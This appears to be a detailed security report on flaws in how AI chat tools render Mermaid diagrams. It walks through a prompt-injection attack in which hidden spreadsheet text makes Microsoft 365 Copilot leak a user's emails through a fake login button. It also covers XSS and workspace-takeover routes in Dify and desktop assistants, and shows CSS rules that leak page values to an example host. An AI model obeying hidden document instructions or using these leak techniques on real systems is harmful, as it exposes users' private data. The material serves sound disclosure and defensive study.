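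SSVC, one of the systems they tested, asks questions such as whether anyone is exploiting the flaw and whether an attacker could automate the attack, rather than producing a number from 0 to 10. The US cybersecurity agency CISA gave the same answers for both Cursor flaws: no exploitation, not automatable, and partial technical impact. The answer on exploitation helps a company decide how urgently to update, but it dates from the first days after each record appeared, and victims would have had difficulty noticing a leak that looked like a request for a picture.

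Many companies still decide what to patch first by severity, but sources can rate the same flaw differently. Tenable's *CVE-2025-54132* lists the first flaw as "high", in line with NVD, while GitHub rated it "medium". A security team relying on GitHub's score could reasonably have left the update until later.

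## Microsoft 365 Copilot: a fake login button inside a diagram

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the AI assistant that Microsoft sells to organisations that use Word, Excel, Outlook and Teams. It can search an employee's emails and files, and in 2025 it could also draw Mermaid diagrams in its answers. The security researcher Adam Logue found that a spreadsheet with hidden instructions could make Copilot gather the user's recent emails and draw a diagram that looked like a login button. Clicking the button sent the emails to the attacker's server. Logue published the attack in October 2025, after Microsoft fixed the flaw.

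Unlike the zero-click leak in Cursor, this attack required the user to click a link, so much of it consisted of giving the user a reason to click.

### From spreadsheet to button

BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) describes the attack in detail:

1. The attacker makes an Excel file with two sheets. The first contains invented financial figures, so the file looks like ordinary office work. Both sheets also contain instructions in white text, which a person looking at a white sheet won't see.
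2. The victim asks Copilot to summarize the file. The model receives the white text along with everything else.
3. The hidden text on the first sheet tells Copilot to look at the second sheet before summarizing. The hidden text there replaces the summary with a different job.
4. Copilot uses a tool called `search_enterprise_emails` to fetch the user's recent emails, and lists their contents as bullet points.
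5. It converts the list into hexadecimal, a code made up of digits and the letters a to f.
6. It tells the user that the document contains sensitive information and that they must log in to see it. Below this it draws a Mermaid diagram styled as a button, with a padlock emoji. The button's link leads to the attacker's server, and the encoded emails are part of the address.
7. The user clicks the button, and the browser sends the whole address to the attacker's server. The attacker copies the code from the server's log and turns it back into text.

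After the click, an iframe showing the server's reply replaced the diagram. Logue made his server reply with a picture of the Microsoft 365 login redirect screen, so that the click looked like the start of a normal login. The user never had to type a password, because the click had already sent the emails to his server. After a few seconds the iframe disappeared from the chat, which removed some of the evidence.

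The iframe suggests that Copilot may already have rendered diagrams in a separate embedded page, as Mermaid's `sandbox` setting does. If it did, that separation didn't stop the link from working.

Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes an earlier attack on Copilot, from 2024, in which a malicious email or shared document made it search the user's other emails without asking for approval. Copilot then displayed a link to the attacker's site, with the stolen data written in invisible characters. Logue's attack used the same kind of search and also ended in a link, but a diagram let the attacker disguise the link as a button that looked like part of Copilot's own controls.

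### Fitting emails into a diagram

Hexadecimal, or hex, represents each byte of text as two characters. An unaccented English letter takes one byte, so the seven letters of "Meeting" become the 14 characters `4d656574696e67`. Most accented letters take two bytes, so they become four characters.

Hex is convenient for an attacker because none of its 16 characters has a special meaning in a web address or a Mermaid label. Emails are full of spaces, quotation marks and brackets, any of which could cut the link short or cause a syntax error. Hex also hides the emails from a user who checks the address before clicking, because they see a long code instead of sentences from their inbox. But anyone can decode hex without a key, so Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) is wrong to call the emails in the link encrypted.

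The drawback is length. According to BeyondMachines, Mermaid allowed only 200 characters per line. Logue's instructions therefore told Copilot to break the code into lines of at most 30 characters, using a backslash to mark each continuation. Suppose one of the emails contains this sentence, which has 60 characters including spaces:

> The board meets on Tuesday at ten to approve the Acme merger

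In hex it has 120 characters, which fill four lines:

```
54686520626f617264206d65657473
206f6e205475657364617920617420
74656e20746f20617070726f766520
7468652041636d65206d6572676572
```

Each line holds 15 characters of the email, and the first decodes to "The board meets". Lines of 200 characters would have held 100, but language models are unreliable at counting characters, and a target of 30 leaves plenty of room for a line that comes out too long.

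Base64, which Rehberger used against Bing Chat, would have needed only 80 characters for the same sentence, but its output can include plus signs, slashes and equals signs, which have special meanings in web addresses.

The length of the code also limits how much an attacker can steal with one click. BeyondMachines illustrates the attack with a user's last 50 emails. With a backslash and a line break on each line, every 15 characters of email take up 32 characters of the diagram. If Copilot kept Mermaid's default limit of 50,000 characters per diagram, one button could hold at most about 23,000 characters of email, or fewer than 470 for each of the 50 messages. That is enough for the subject lines and the first few sentences, but not for long conversations. A password or the news of a merger would still fit easily.

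### Changing the task by degrees

Logue's instructions moved Copilot away from the user's request in stages, unlike the blunt command hidden in the job applicant's CV. The white text on the first sheet was an instruction to read the second sheet before summarizing, which is close to what the user wanted. Real spreadsheets often contain notes pointing to another sheet, and a good summary would take them into account. The instructions to replace the summary with a demand to log in appeared only on the second sheet.

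Logue settled on this wording after extensive testing, according to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, and took inspiration from TaskTracker, a Microsoft research project on detecting prompt injection. *Get my drift?* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2024) presents the project's method and defines "task drift" as any change in what a model is doing that comes from the outside text it reads. For example, a user might ask for a summary, and a sentence in the document might make the model write a poem. The researchers count even a harmless poem as a security failure, because a model should never take orders from a document.

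The paper splits an injection into a trigger and a payload. The payload is the instruction that the attacker wants the model to follow, and the trigger is a sentence that prepares the model to follow it. The researchers had GPT-4 write many triggers, from subtle hints that instructions were coming to warnings in capital letters. In Logue's file, the note on the first sheet acts as the trigger, and the second sheet contains the payload.

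TaskTracker looks for drift in a model's activations, the numbers it computes internally while processing text. Applied to Logue's file, the method would work like this:

1. The detector gives the model only the user's request to summarize the file. It adds a prompt asking the model to list the requests it is about to carry out, and records the activations before the model writes anything.
2. It repeats this with the request and the file together.
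3. It subtracts the first set of activations from the second. A small classifier, which has learned from many clean and poisoned documents, judges whether the difference looks like a new task.

The researchers trained the classifier only on ordinary tasks, such as trivia questions, inserted into paragraphs from sources like Wikipedia. They then tested it on jailbreaks and malicious instructions that were not in its training data. On all six models they tried, it scored over 0.99, where 1 is perfect and 0.5 is guessing. More than 99% of the time, it rated a random poisoned example as more suspicious than a random clean one.

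A gradual approach might not defeat such a detector. TaskTracker compares the model's task before it reads the file with its task afterwards, and the change from writing a summary to searching a mailbox is large, however small the steps in between. A gradual approach seems more useful against the model's own resistance, or against a filter that looks for stock phrases such as "ignore previous instructions".

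However, Abdelnabi and colleagues found that their detector flagged a question more readily when it was phrased as a direct instruction than when it occurred naturally in the text. A hidden note that reads like part of the spreadsheet might therefore be harder to detect, at least until the model reaches the second sheet. They inserted only one task into each test document, so their results don't show how well the method handles instructions that lead from one sheet to another. The paper also doesn't show that Copilot had such a detector when Logue attacked it.

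### The user had to click

Logue's attack was a one-click leak. The user had to ask Copilot for a summary, which is ordinary use, and then click the button. In *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability*, gnabgib quotes Logue's summary of the attack, in which the emails reach the attacker's server "when clicked".

Several accounts misdescribe the user's role in the attack. OffSeq's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* says that the "lack of authentication or user interaction requirements" makes the flaw more dangerous, which is wrong because the user has to click the login button. Cyber Security News writes that the theft needed no direct interaction "beyond an initial click", and Red Hot Cyber also writes of a "single initial click". Both articles describe the button correctly and note that Copilot, unlike Cursor, required the user to do something. But "initial click" suggests that the user clicks at the start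 and the rest happens automatically. The click actually comes last, after Copilot has searched the mailbox and written the emails into a link, and nothing is sent to the attacker if the user ignores the button.

The mistake matters to anyone judging how serious the flaw was, because a required click lowers a flaw's CVSS score.

Even so, requiring a click gave users little protection. People who use Microsoft 365 at work log in often, and a request to log in before seeing a sensitive document is plausible. Phishing training usually covers unexpected emails and unfamiliar websites, not replies from the employer's own assistant. A careful user might have wondered why a file that was already open needed another login. BeyondMachines recommends training employees to recognise such tricks and checking where documents come from. This is reasonable advice, but it relies heavily on the judgement of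 people who are only asking for a summary.

### Six weeks from report to fix

At the DEF CON hacking conference in August 2025, Logue discussed the problem with staff of the Microsoft Security Response Center (MSRC), which handles reports from outside researchers. He sent them the full attack on 15 August. Cyber Security News reports that Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first and Logue supplied videos as proof. MSRC confirmed the flaw on 8 September and had resolved it by 26 September.

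A conventional software flaw usually behaves the same way every time, but a language model can respond differently to the same file. Copilot also had to complete five steps: read the second sheet, search the mailbox, encode the result, write valid Mermaid and put the right address in the link. As an illustration, if each step independently worked 90% of the time, the whole attack would work about 59% of the time. At 70% per step, it would work only about 17% of the time, and an engineer who tried it twice would probably see two failures and could mistake a real flaw for a false alarm. Microsoft now asks researchers who report flaws in its consumer Copilot to include a conversation ID, which identifies the chat in which the attack worked.

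The fix removed interactive links from the diagrams that Copilot drew. daily.dev describes the change more broadly, saying it removed the ability to interact with "dynamic content" in a diagram. Either way, hidden text could still have made Copilot search the mailbox and draw a login button, but clicking the button would no longer have done anything. Users lost little, since a flowchart is nearly as useful without links.

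Remote images had caused the leak in Cursor, but the fix doesn't show whether Copilot allowed them in diagrams. Copilot may already have blocked them, since this attack relied on persuading someone to click, which an attacker who could load an image wouldn't need to do.

BeyondMachines doubted that the patch covered every way of exploiting the flaw. The patch also left open other ways to send data out of the product. On 16 October 2025, 20 days after the fix, Rehberger reported a leak through Copilot's previews of HTML pages. *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot* (Underhill, 2026) described a one-click leak, and *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported three zero-click methods, collectively named ReLeak.

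### No bounty

Microsoft did not pay Logue for the report. Its bug bounty programmes reward outside researchers for reporting flaws in particular products, but no programme covered Microsoft 365 Copilot.

Microsoft's *Copilot Bounty Program* covers only the consumer assistant, including its website, its phone app and its versions for WhatsApp and Telegram. In March 2025, five months before Logue's report, Microsoft clarified the rules to tell researchers to test with a personal account, whereas Microsoft 365 Copilot is for people with a work or school account.

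Microsoft has another programme for its online office services, the *M365 Bounty Program*, whose current list includes Outlook, Exchange, Teams and SharePoint, but not Copilot. A researcher who finds a way to steal emails can therefore qualify under that programme if the flaw is in Outlook's online version, but not if it is in Copilot.

Logue's report also arrived during a promotion. From 4 August to 4 October, Microsoft (2025) offered multiplied awards for certain flaws in a list of products that included both "Copilot" and "M365". A researcher could easily have read that list as including Microsoft 365 Copilot, but Logue received no award.

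Microsoft changed its bounty rules in December 2025 with a policy called "In Scope by Default". According to *Evolving our approach to coordinated security research* (2025), a critical vulnerability in any Microsoft online service can earn an award, even if no bounty programme covers that service. The policy also applies to flaws in third-party code that affect those services, including open-source code such as Mermaid. But it promises awards only for critical vulnerabilities, and there is no public indication that Microsoft rated Logue's finding as critical.

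Soon afterwards, Microsoft did pay for a flaw in the same product. According to Embrace The Red, it paid Rehberger a bounty on 17 December 2025 for the HTML preview leak. He had reported the leak in October, before the new policy, so the payment suggests that Microsoft had become more willing to reward work on Microsoft 365 Copilot, but it doesn't show that the policy was the reason.

From 17 February to 18 March 2026, Microsoft ran a separate bounty programme for Microsoft 365 Copilot, including the versions built into Excel, Word, Outlook and Teams. It offered between $250 and $30,000 for flaws and was limited to participants in an invitation-only hacking event. For flaws that disclosed private information, the highest listed awards were $8,000 for critical ones and $4,000 for important ones, the next level down.

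Logue's attack might still have led to a dispute over eligibility, because the rules excluded flaws that need "extensive or unlikely user actions". One click on a login button is not extensive, and the attack was designed to make that click likely. The rules also excluded types of vulnerability that Microsoft was already investigating broad defences against. That exclusion could cover much of prompt injection if interpreted in Microsoft's favour.

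ITPro's *Microsoft forks out record-breaking sums with expanded bug bounty program* reports that Microsoft's total bounty payments have since grown from $17 million for 344 researchers in one year to more than $20 million for 562 the next, partly because of the new policy. But the temporary programme for Microsoft 365 Copilot has ended, and the two permanent ones still leave it out. To be paid for a similar flaw now, a researcher would have to show that it was critical, or hope for an award under Microsoft's Standard Award Policy, which can cover reports outside a particular programme.

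## Dify and other open-source chat applications

In Dify, an open-source platform for building chatbots, clicking a diagram could run an attacker's script in the user's browser, whereas in Microsoft 365 Copilot it sent data to an attacker's server. Snyk described the Dify flaw in March 2026. Several other open-source chat applications have had similar flaws, often because they rendered diagrams with `loose`, Mermaid's most permissive setting.

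### A filter with gaps

Dify's developers knew that `loose` was risky. When they switched to it from the sandbox, which had interfered with colour themes, they relied on their own filter to catch dangerous links. Before passing a diagram to Mermaid, Dify searched the text for clickable nodes whose link began with `javascript:`, the prefix that marks the rest of a link as a script, and replaced any such link with a `#`, which leads nowhere.

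Snyk found that Dify prepared the text of Gantt charts (timelines of tasks), mind maps and sequence diagrams (which show messages passing between people or programs) differently from other diagrams, and didn't filter it. Tasks in a Gantt chart can have links too, so an attacker could get past the filter by using a Gantt chart instead of a flowchart.

The filter seems to have missed some flowchart links as well. Mermaid accepts a link in two forms:

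```
click B "https://example.com/rsvp"
click B href "https://example.com/rsvp"
```

The search pattern Snyk quotes requires a quotation mark immediately after the node's name, so it matches only the first form. Snyk doesn't mention this gap, but its demonstration against a public chatbot used a flowchart with the second form, as did the demonstration in Dify's security advisory (2026).

### An attack by the chatbot's owner

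Someone who types a malicious diagram into their own chat only attacks their own browser, which security researchers call self-XSS and usually consider harmless. Snyk looked for a way to reach other people and found it in Dify's public chatbots:

1. The attacker builds a chatbot in Dify. In its settings, they tell the model to answer every message with a particular diagram.
2. They publish the chatbot, and a visitor sends it a message.
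3. The model writes the diagram, and Dify draws it in the visitor's browser. Snyk's example had a single node that invited the visitor to follow a link to a project.
4. The visitor clicks the node, and the script in the link runs as part of Dify's page.

The attacker here is the chatbot's developer, whose instructions the model is supposed to follow. The attack therefore doesn't need a prompt injection, and training a model to ignore commands hidden in documents would not help. Dify's advisory describes another route, in which the attacker puts the diagram in a chat and shares the chat with the victim. Both are stored XSS, meaning the application saves the malicious content and later delivers it to other people.

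### What a script can do that an address cannot

An image address can carry only data that the model has seen and copied into it. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, a security researcher who publishes as veganmosfet used the Markdown image leak in Dify to steal a user's name. The researcher hid the instructions in a PDF file that the chatbot consulted.

A script can collect data without the model's help. It can read whatever the page displays and request more from Dify's server. The browser attaches the user's login to these requests, so the server treats them as the user's own. The script can then read the replies and send them to the attacker, using as many requests as it needs. Logue's attack on Copilot was more limited because it relied on the model to see the data, copy it accurately and fit it into one address.

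A script can also make changes to a workspace. *XSS in Dify could lead to Workspace Takeover* (veganmosfet, 2026) showed this using a separate flaw in how Dify drew charts with ECharts, another JavaScript library. A visitor to a chatbot types in a chart description that contains a script. When the workspace owner opens the conversation log, Dify draws the chart again and the script runs with the owner's login. The script makes Dify invite the attacker's email address as an administrator. Dify then emails the attacker an invitation code, and the owner notices nothing.

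Dify had taken the common precaution of blocking scripts from reading the owner's login cookie, so the attacker couldn't steal the cookie and log in from another computer. But the browser still attached the cookie to the script's request. Dify also required a token proving that the request came from one of its own pages, but scripts could read that token.

The chart's script ran as soon as the chart appeared, whereas the Mermaid flaw needed a click. After the click, a script in a diagram should have had much the same access as the chart's script. A stranger without a Dify account who clicked might lose only the contents of the chat, while an administrator logged in to the same site could lose the workspace.

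### The return to strict

Dify fixed the Mermaid flaw in version 1.11.2 by switching Mermaid from `loose` to `strict`. This is more reliable than the filter because Mermaid itself disables clicking, so Dify's developers don't have to anticipate every way of writing a link. When programmers have to add cleaning separately in each place, they can easily miss one. According to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-41318* (2026), the chat application AnythingLLM ran its formatted text through DOMPurify everywhere except in chart captions, and a prompt injection could exploit the omission.

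Dify published the flaw as CVE-2026-21866 on 3 March 2026, two days before Snyk's article. OSV's *CVE-2026-21866* (2026) gives it a score of 5.1 out of 10 under CVSS version 4. Dify's advisory uses the older version 3.1 and rates the possible loss of private data as high but the possible alteration of data as none. The rating for alteration looks wrong, because veganmosfet's script could add an administrator.

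The two sources also differ on which versions had the flaw. The advisory names only 1.10.1, while OSV lists every release from 0.2.1 to 1.11.1. OSV's list is probably too long, because it treats the flaw as always present, even though Dify once used the sandbox.

Dify 1.11.2 still had the ECharts flaw, CVE-2026-26023, which remained until version 1.13.0. The flaw affected only people who ran Dify on their own servers and had left the CSP setting blank, in which case Dify applies no CSP. Snyk points out that a strict CSP can block JavaScript links even when an application fails to remove them.

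A blank CSP also leaves images unrestricted, so a patched copy of Dify could leak data through image nodes even under `strict`, if its version of Mermaid supports them.

### Open WebUI and LibreChat

Open WebUI is a chat application that people run on their own servers. More than three months after Snyk's article, NVD's *CVE-2026-54011* (2026) described a flaw in it with the same cause. Open WebUI's preview for Markdown files drew any Mermaid diagrams in them with the `loose` setting.

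Corgea's *Open WebUI* reproduces the advisory, which demonstrates the attack by uploading a Markdown file, opening the preview and clicking a node. The attack doesn't involve the language model, because the diagram is already in the file. An attacker would only have to get the file to a user and persuade them to click. The advisory recommended the `strict` setting, and Open WebUI fixed the flaw in version 0.9.6. Corgea lists the flaw's severity as 8.7, much higher than Dify's 5.1 for nearly the same mistake.

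Other flaws in Open WebUI suggest how much damage a script could do there. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-70492* describes a flaw that let a script in a mathematical formula steal the user's session token, which proves they are logged in, because Open WebUI kept it where scripts could read it. The attacker could then take over the account. If the victim is an administrator, the attacker may also be able to take control of the server. According to OSV's *GHSA-9f4f-jv96-8766*, which concerns another XSS flaw, administrators can add Python functions, so a script running with an administrator's access can add one that runs malicious code on the server.

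LibreChat, a similar application, also draws Mermaid diagrams. Vulners' *CVE-2025-7105* describes a LibreChat flaw that could make the server run out of memory if a user copied, many times in quick succession, a conversation containing a diagram with a very large number of nodes. This could interrupt the service but wouldn't reveal anyone's data. In *CGA-65jm-m32v-3743*, the software supplier Chainguard also lists its LibreChat package under one of the flaws in Mermaid's styling code.

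### Why a script reaches further on the desktop

A browser keeps a website's scripts away from the rest of the computer. A script on Dify's page can misuse the victim's Dify account, but it can't open the files on their disk or start a program.

Many desktop chat applications use Electron, a framework for building desktop programs with web technology. Their windows work like web pages and run JavaScript, but the Electron project warns developers that Electron is not a web browser and that JavaScript can reach the user's files and command shell.

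*DeepChat AI agent XSS-to-RCE via Mermaid and Electron IPC* (Stefani, 2025) describes a vulnerability in DeepChat, an open-source desktop assistant built on Electron. Electron applications have a renderer process, which displays the window, and a more privileged main process, which deals with the operating system. The two exchange messages through inter-process communication (IPC). A careful developer lets the page in the window send only a few specific messages, but DeepChat gave it the whole IPC object, so a script in a diagram could request any action the application was able to perform.

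The AI assistant DeepChat connects to outside tools through MCP, and some of those tools are programs that it starts on the user's computer. According to *CVE-2025-66222* (2025), from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, a script in a Mermaid diagram could register a malicious MCP server and start it. Starting programs was one of DeepChat's normal functions, so the attacker didn't need to break into the operating system. The attacker could then read saved conversations, API keys and local files, and run any command that the user could.

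DeepChat's developers had to fix its Mermaid diagrams several times:

- Version 0.3.5 fixed an early flaw. OSV's *CVE-2025-58768* blames it on an incomplete repair of an older XSS problem, which had left diagrams as another way to reach the IPC object.
- On 3 December 2025 a new record, the one that INCIBE reproduces, reported that a script in a diagram could still take control of the computer in version 0.5.0. It scored 9.6.
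- Five days later, NVD's *CVE-2025-66481* reported that the latest patch didn't work. DeepChat had added a text filter to remove dangerous HTML attributes, and an attacker could get around it. Version 0.5.1 was vulnerable, and no fix was available yet.
- On 15 December, NVD's *CVE-2025-67744* (2025) named two causes, the unsafe Mermaid configuration and the exposed IPC object, and gave 0.5.3 as the patched version.

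The text filter failed because the browser interpreted the same characters differently. In HTML, a letter can be written as a numeric code, so `&#99;at` means "cat". A filter searching for "cat" misses the encoded version, but the browser decodes it and displays the word. An attacker could disguise a forbidden attribute's contents this way, and could also omit the quotation marks the filter looked for. DeepChat again made a similar mistake when handling SVG drawings. OSV's *CVE-2026-43900* describes a filter that searched for JavaScript links as plain text and missed encoded ones. DeepChat fixed the flaw in version 1.0.4-beta.1.

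Stefani recommends disabling scripts and interactive features in diagrams unless the application needs them, and never giving the page direct access to IPC. Restricting IPC matters even with those features disabled, because a program that displays so many kinds of content is likely to have another XSS flaw, and the restriction limits what an injected script can do.

### LobeChat and 5ire

LobeChat, which has web and desktop versions, had almost the same combination of flaws. According to OSV's *GHSA-4gpc-rhpj-9443* (2026), it passed diagrams to Mermaid without cleaning them, and Mermaid put HTML from the labels straight into the page. Mermaid's default setting should have encoded that HTML, so LobeChat was probably using a weaker one. The demonstration put a broken image in a label, with a script that ran when the image failed to load. The script used LobeChat's MCP feature to open the computer's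 calculator, a traditional, harmless way to prove that an attacker could run any program. Unlike the Dify flaw, this one didn't require a click on the diagram.

In the demonstration, the user asked the model to repeat the malicious diagram word for word, which no victim would knowingly do. But a prompt injection could also put the diagram into a chat. GitLab's *CVE-2025-59417* (2025) notes the same possibility for an earlier LobeChat flaw that didn't involve Mermaid.

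LobeChat fixed the Mermaid flaw in version 2.0.0-next.180. OSV lists the flaw's severity as 9.6, while INCIBE's *CVE-2026-23733* (2026) lists it as 6.4, even though both describe an attacker running commands on the victim's computer.

The desktop assistant 5ire set Mermaid to `loose` in its Markdown display code. NVD's *CVE-2025-68669* describes the result as remote code execution in version 0.15.2 and earlier, with no patch at the time. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-68669* (2025) repeats that description, but its list of vulnerable versions excludes 0.15.2, so users can't tell from these records whether that version is safe. NVD's *CVE-2026-22793* reports that version 0.15.3 fixed a similar flaw in 5ire's ECharts diagrams, but doesn't mention Mermaid.

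## Mermaid's own styling flaws, fixed in May 2026

Dify protected its users by switching Mermaid to `strict`. That setting did not help against a group of flaws that became public on 11 May 2026, because they were in how Mermaid itself handled styles. Two of them let a diagram add CSS rules that applied to the whole page. Such rules can reveal the page's contents, including data the model never received.

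### How styles escaped from the diagram

A CSS rule has two parts:

```
#plan .late { fill: pink; }
```

The selector, the part before the braces, determines which elements the rule applies to, and the part inside the braces sets how they look. Mermaid gives each diagram an ID, here `plan`, and puts it at the front of the diagram's selectors, so this rule colours anything marked `late` inside the diagram without affecting the rest of the page.

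In CVE-2026-41148, a style definition could break out of its own rule. OSV's *GHSA-xcj9-5m2h-648r* (2026) traces the mistake through Mermaid's code:

1. A state diagram defines a style with `classDef`. Mermaid accepts everything after the style's name, up to the end of the line.
2. Mermaid writes a selector and an opening brace, pastes in the text it accepted, and adds a closing brace.
3. If the pasted text contains a closing brace of its own, the browser takes that as the end of the rule.
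4. The browser reads whatever follows as a new rule. The attacker wrote the new rule's selector, so it can apply to any part of the page.

SQL injection exploits much the same mistake. Text meant to be a value ends the value early and continues as a command. The Mermaid flaw also affected any other diagram type that passed its styles through the same function.

CVE-2026-41159 was in the font and theme settings. Mermaid uses a library called stylis to add the diagram's ID to each selector. In stylis's notation, an ampersand stands for the diagram, so an attacker could write a selector meaning "everything except the diagram". Stylis replaced the ampersand with the ID, producing a valid rule for the rest of the page. It also moved some kinds of rule, including those that define new fonts, outside the diagram's scope. OSV credits the discovery to a researcher at Tencent's Keen Security Lab.

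Mermaid had fixed a similar flaw in June 2022, two weeks after GitHub Security Lab reported it. An attacker could exploit that flaw through the text colour setting. The code quoted in the report inserted the font setting in the same way, two lines earlier, and the report encouraged the developers to look for other places where an attacker could add rules. Four years later, the font setting was one of the ways to exploit CVE-2026-41159.

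### How a style rule reveals a value

Suppose a chat application's page records the user's role in an attribute, a named value attached to an HTML element. The attribute is called `data-role`, and its value is either `admin` or `member`. An attacker who can add styles to the page adds two rules:

```
body:has([data-role="admin"])  { background-image: url("https://example.com/a.png"); }
body:has([data-role="member"]) { background-image: url("https://example.com/m.png"); }
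```

The browser then does the following:

1. It checks whether the page contains an element whose `data-role` is `admin`. This user is an administrator, so the first rule applies.
2. It checks for `member`, finds nothing, and ignores the second rule.
3. It requests `a.png` from example.com to use as the page's background.

The server's log now has a request for `a.png`, so the attacker knows the user is an administrator. The attacker wrote both addresses beforehand, and neither contains any private data. The user's role determines which one the browser requests, and the user doesn't have to click anything.

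In these rules, `:has()` makes the style of one element depend on another element inside it. This helps an attacker because pages often keep values in hidden fields, and a browser normally doesn't load a background for an element it isn't displaying. With `:has()`, the attacker can put the background on a visible part of the page instead.

An attacker could find a longer value, such as a six-digit code, one digit at a time with ten rules for each, but each round needs a new set of styles. Woltjer's *CSS Injection* describes a way to find the whole value with one set of styles, using rules that test whether it contains certain characters anywhere. An attacker could test for each of the 100 possible pairs of digits. If the requests show that the code contains 48, 82, 29, 91 and 13, it must be 482913, because those pairs overlap in only one order.

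This becomes impractical inside a diagram as the value gets more complicated. Lowercase letters and digits make 1,296 possible pairs. At 50 characters per rule, testing for all of them would take about 65,000 characters, which is over Mermaid's default limit for one diagram. An attacker who relies on prompt injection also needs the model to write all those rules correctly. Short codes and values with few possibilities are much easier targets, though an attacker could spread a longer search over several diagrams.

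### What styles can and cannot read

Attributes are the easiest target. They can hold link addresses, tooltip text, account numbers, and the tokens that websites use to check that a form came from their own page. *Blind CSS Exfiltration*, from the web security testing company PortSwigger, demonstrates how to extract data from a page without knowing how it is built. The method is meant for sites that block scripts but allow styles, for instance because they clean their HTML with DOMPurify, as Mermaid does.

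Text that a user types into a box is usually safer. According to Archibald's *Third party CSS is not safe*, browsers don't copy typed text into the field's `value` attribute by default, so a style rule that tests the attribute won't match it. But some websites use frameworks such as React that update the attribute to match the typed text, and on those sites a style rule can pick up a password as the user types it.

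Ordinary text on the page, which includes most of a conversation with an assistant, is harder for an attacker to read because CSS selectors can't test for words. An attacker can use fonts instead. A font definition can specify which characters the font covers, and the browser downloads the font only if it needs one of them. An attacker who defines a separate font for the pound sign can find out whether the page contains one, though not where it appears or what amount follows it. A collection of attack techniques on dotya.ml lists tools that recover whole passages, one using ligatures (single shapes that a font substitutes for a sequence of letters) and another using scrollbars. The two Mermaid advisories mention only the theft of attributes, so it is uncertain whether these tools would have worked through a diagram.

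Styles cannot directly read cookies or the browser's local storage, as sibivasan's *CSS Injection to Data Exfiltration* notes. They also normally cannot read any page except the one they are on. A malicious style in a chat window could therefore test the attributes in that window but could not read the user's email in another tab, so it is much weaker than the script in the Dify attack.

Conditional rules are a clumsy way to steal the conversation if the attacker already controls the model, because the model can write the information it has been given directly into an address. The rules are more useful for stealing what the application puts on the page without giving it to the model, such as the user's account details or links to their other chats. They also work without a model if the attacker can show the victim a finished diagram, perhaps in a shared file.

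### The `strict` setting made no difference

According to OSV's advisory, the font and theme flaw affects Mermaid's default configuration, which uses the `strict` security level. The advisory for CVE-2026-41148 doesn't mention the default, but the only workaround it gives is `sandbox`. If `strict` had been enough, most applications would have been safe already. `strict` restricts HTML and clicks, but an attacker can add a CSS rule without using either.

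A related flaw, CVE-2026-41149, bypassed even the protection against HTML. According to OSV's *GHSA-ghcm-xqfw-q4vr* (2026), the `classDef` instruction in a state diagram could end the drawing and add HTML to the page outside it, again in the default configuration. Mermaid removed scripts, but the demonstration still covered the whole window with a black panel and a message of the attacker's choice. In a chat assistant, such a panel could imitate a login screen, as Logue's button did in Copilot.

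An application that had moved to `strict`, as Dify had, still had good protection against links that run scripts, but it also had to update Mermaid or contain the styles another way. The `sandbox` setting contains them by putting the diagram on its own page, where its style rules can't match anything in the chat window. The sandbox can still load images, so it doesn't necessarily prevent users from being tracked through background images, another effect that OSV lists for CVE-2026-41148.

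OSV's second workaround for CVE-2026-41159 is to add `fontFamily`, `altFontFamily`, `themeCSS` and `themeVariables` to Mermaid's list of protected settings. This doesn't help with `classDef`, which is part of the diagram rather than a setting.

### What the updates changed

Mermaid fixed all three flaws in versions 10.9.6 and 11.15.0. The release notes, which NewReleases' *github mermaid-js/mermaid mermaid@11.15.0* reproduces, list four relevant changes. Mermaid now:

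- prevents style definitions with unbalanced braces or similar errors;
- builds styles through the browser's own interface for CSS rules, where it used to paste text into the page;
- handles the ampersand when it adds the diagram's ID to selectors;
- refuses some of the special rules that begin with an @ sign, the group that includes font definitions.

NewReleases' *npm mermaid 10.9.6*, which has the notes for the older branch, links the first change to CVE-2026-41148, the second to the HTML flaw and the third to CVE-2026-41159. It also lists a fix for Gantt charts that could freeze the page.

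None of these changes restricts which URLs a style may contain. The updates make it much harder for a diagram to read the page, but a CSS rule that applies only inside the diagram can probably still load a background image from any server. An application still needs another way to block that request, such as a CSP that covers both images and fonts.

Keeping styles inside the diagram is still worthwhile, because there is little to steal there. PortSwigger's *Inline Style Exfiltration* shows that even an inline style can make the browser request a different address depending on its element's attributes. In a Mermaid diagram, those attributes mostly come from whoever wrote the diagram, so the attacker would learn little new.

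GitHub scored each of the three flaws 5.3 out of 10 ("medium") under CVSS version 4. GitLab's *CVE-2026-41148* (2026) gives the first one 7.1 ("high") under version 3.1. Unlike the two scores for Cursor, these reflect similar judgements about the attack. GitHub and GitLab both rated it as easy, with some action needed from the user, and rated the possible loss of private data as low. GitLab's score is higher partly because version 3.1 adds points when the damage spreads beyond the flawed component, and would otherwise be 6.3. The "low" rating for data loss seems fair for a page whose attributes contain nothing important, but not for one that keeps a login token in them.

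The official description of CVE-2026-41148 also has an error that could mislead someone deciding whether to update. NVD's *CVE-2026-41148* gives 11.12.0 as the last affected version in the 11 series, while the original advisory correctly gives 11.14.0. The fix came only in 11.15.0, and OSV's *CVE-2026-41148* (2026) lists the five releases between 11.12.0 and 11.15.0 as affected.

### Another escape in August

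After the May updates, a style rule could still reach elements next to the diagram, according to CVE-2026-50159, a record published on 6 August 2026. CSS has symbols for selecting an element's neighbours, so a selector could begin with the diagram's ID, as Mermaid required, and then select elements that came after the diagram in the same container. OSV's *CVE-2026-50159* (2026) lists 11.15.0 and 10.9.6 among the affected versions.

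Docker Scout's *CVE-2026-50159* says that most users of Mermaid were not at risk, because the library normally puts each drawing alone in its own container. Applications were at risk if they inserted the drawing themselves, next to other elements. A chat application might do this to put a "copy" or "zoom" button beside each diagram. An attacker could then hide or restyle those elements, or use conditional rules to test what they contained. They would usually contain less information than the whole page.

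| Flaw | What a diagram could do | Fixed in | Workarounds |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-41148 | Add styles for the whole page through `classDef` | 10.9.6 and 11.15.0 | `sandbox` |
| CVE-2026-41149 | Add HTML without scripts outside the drawing through `classDef` | 10.9.6 and 11.15.0 | `sandbox` |
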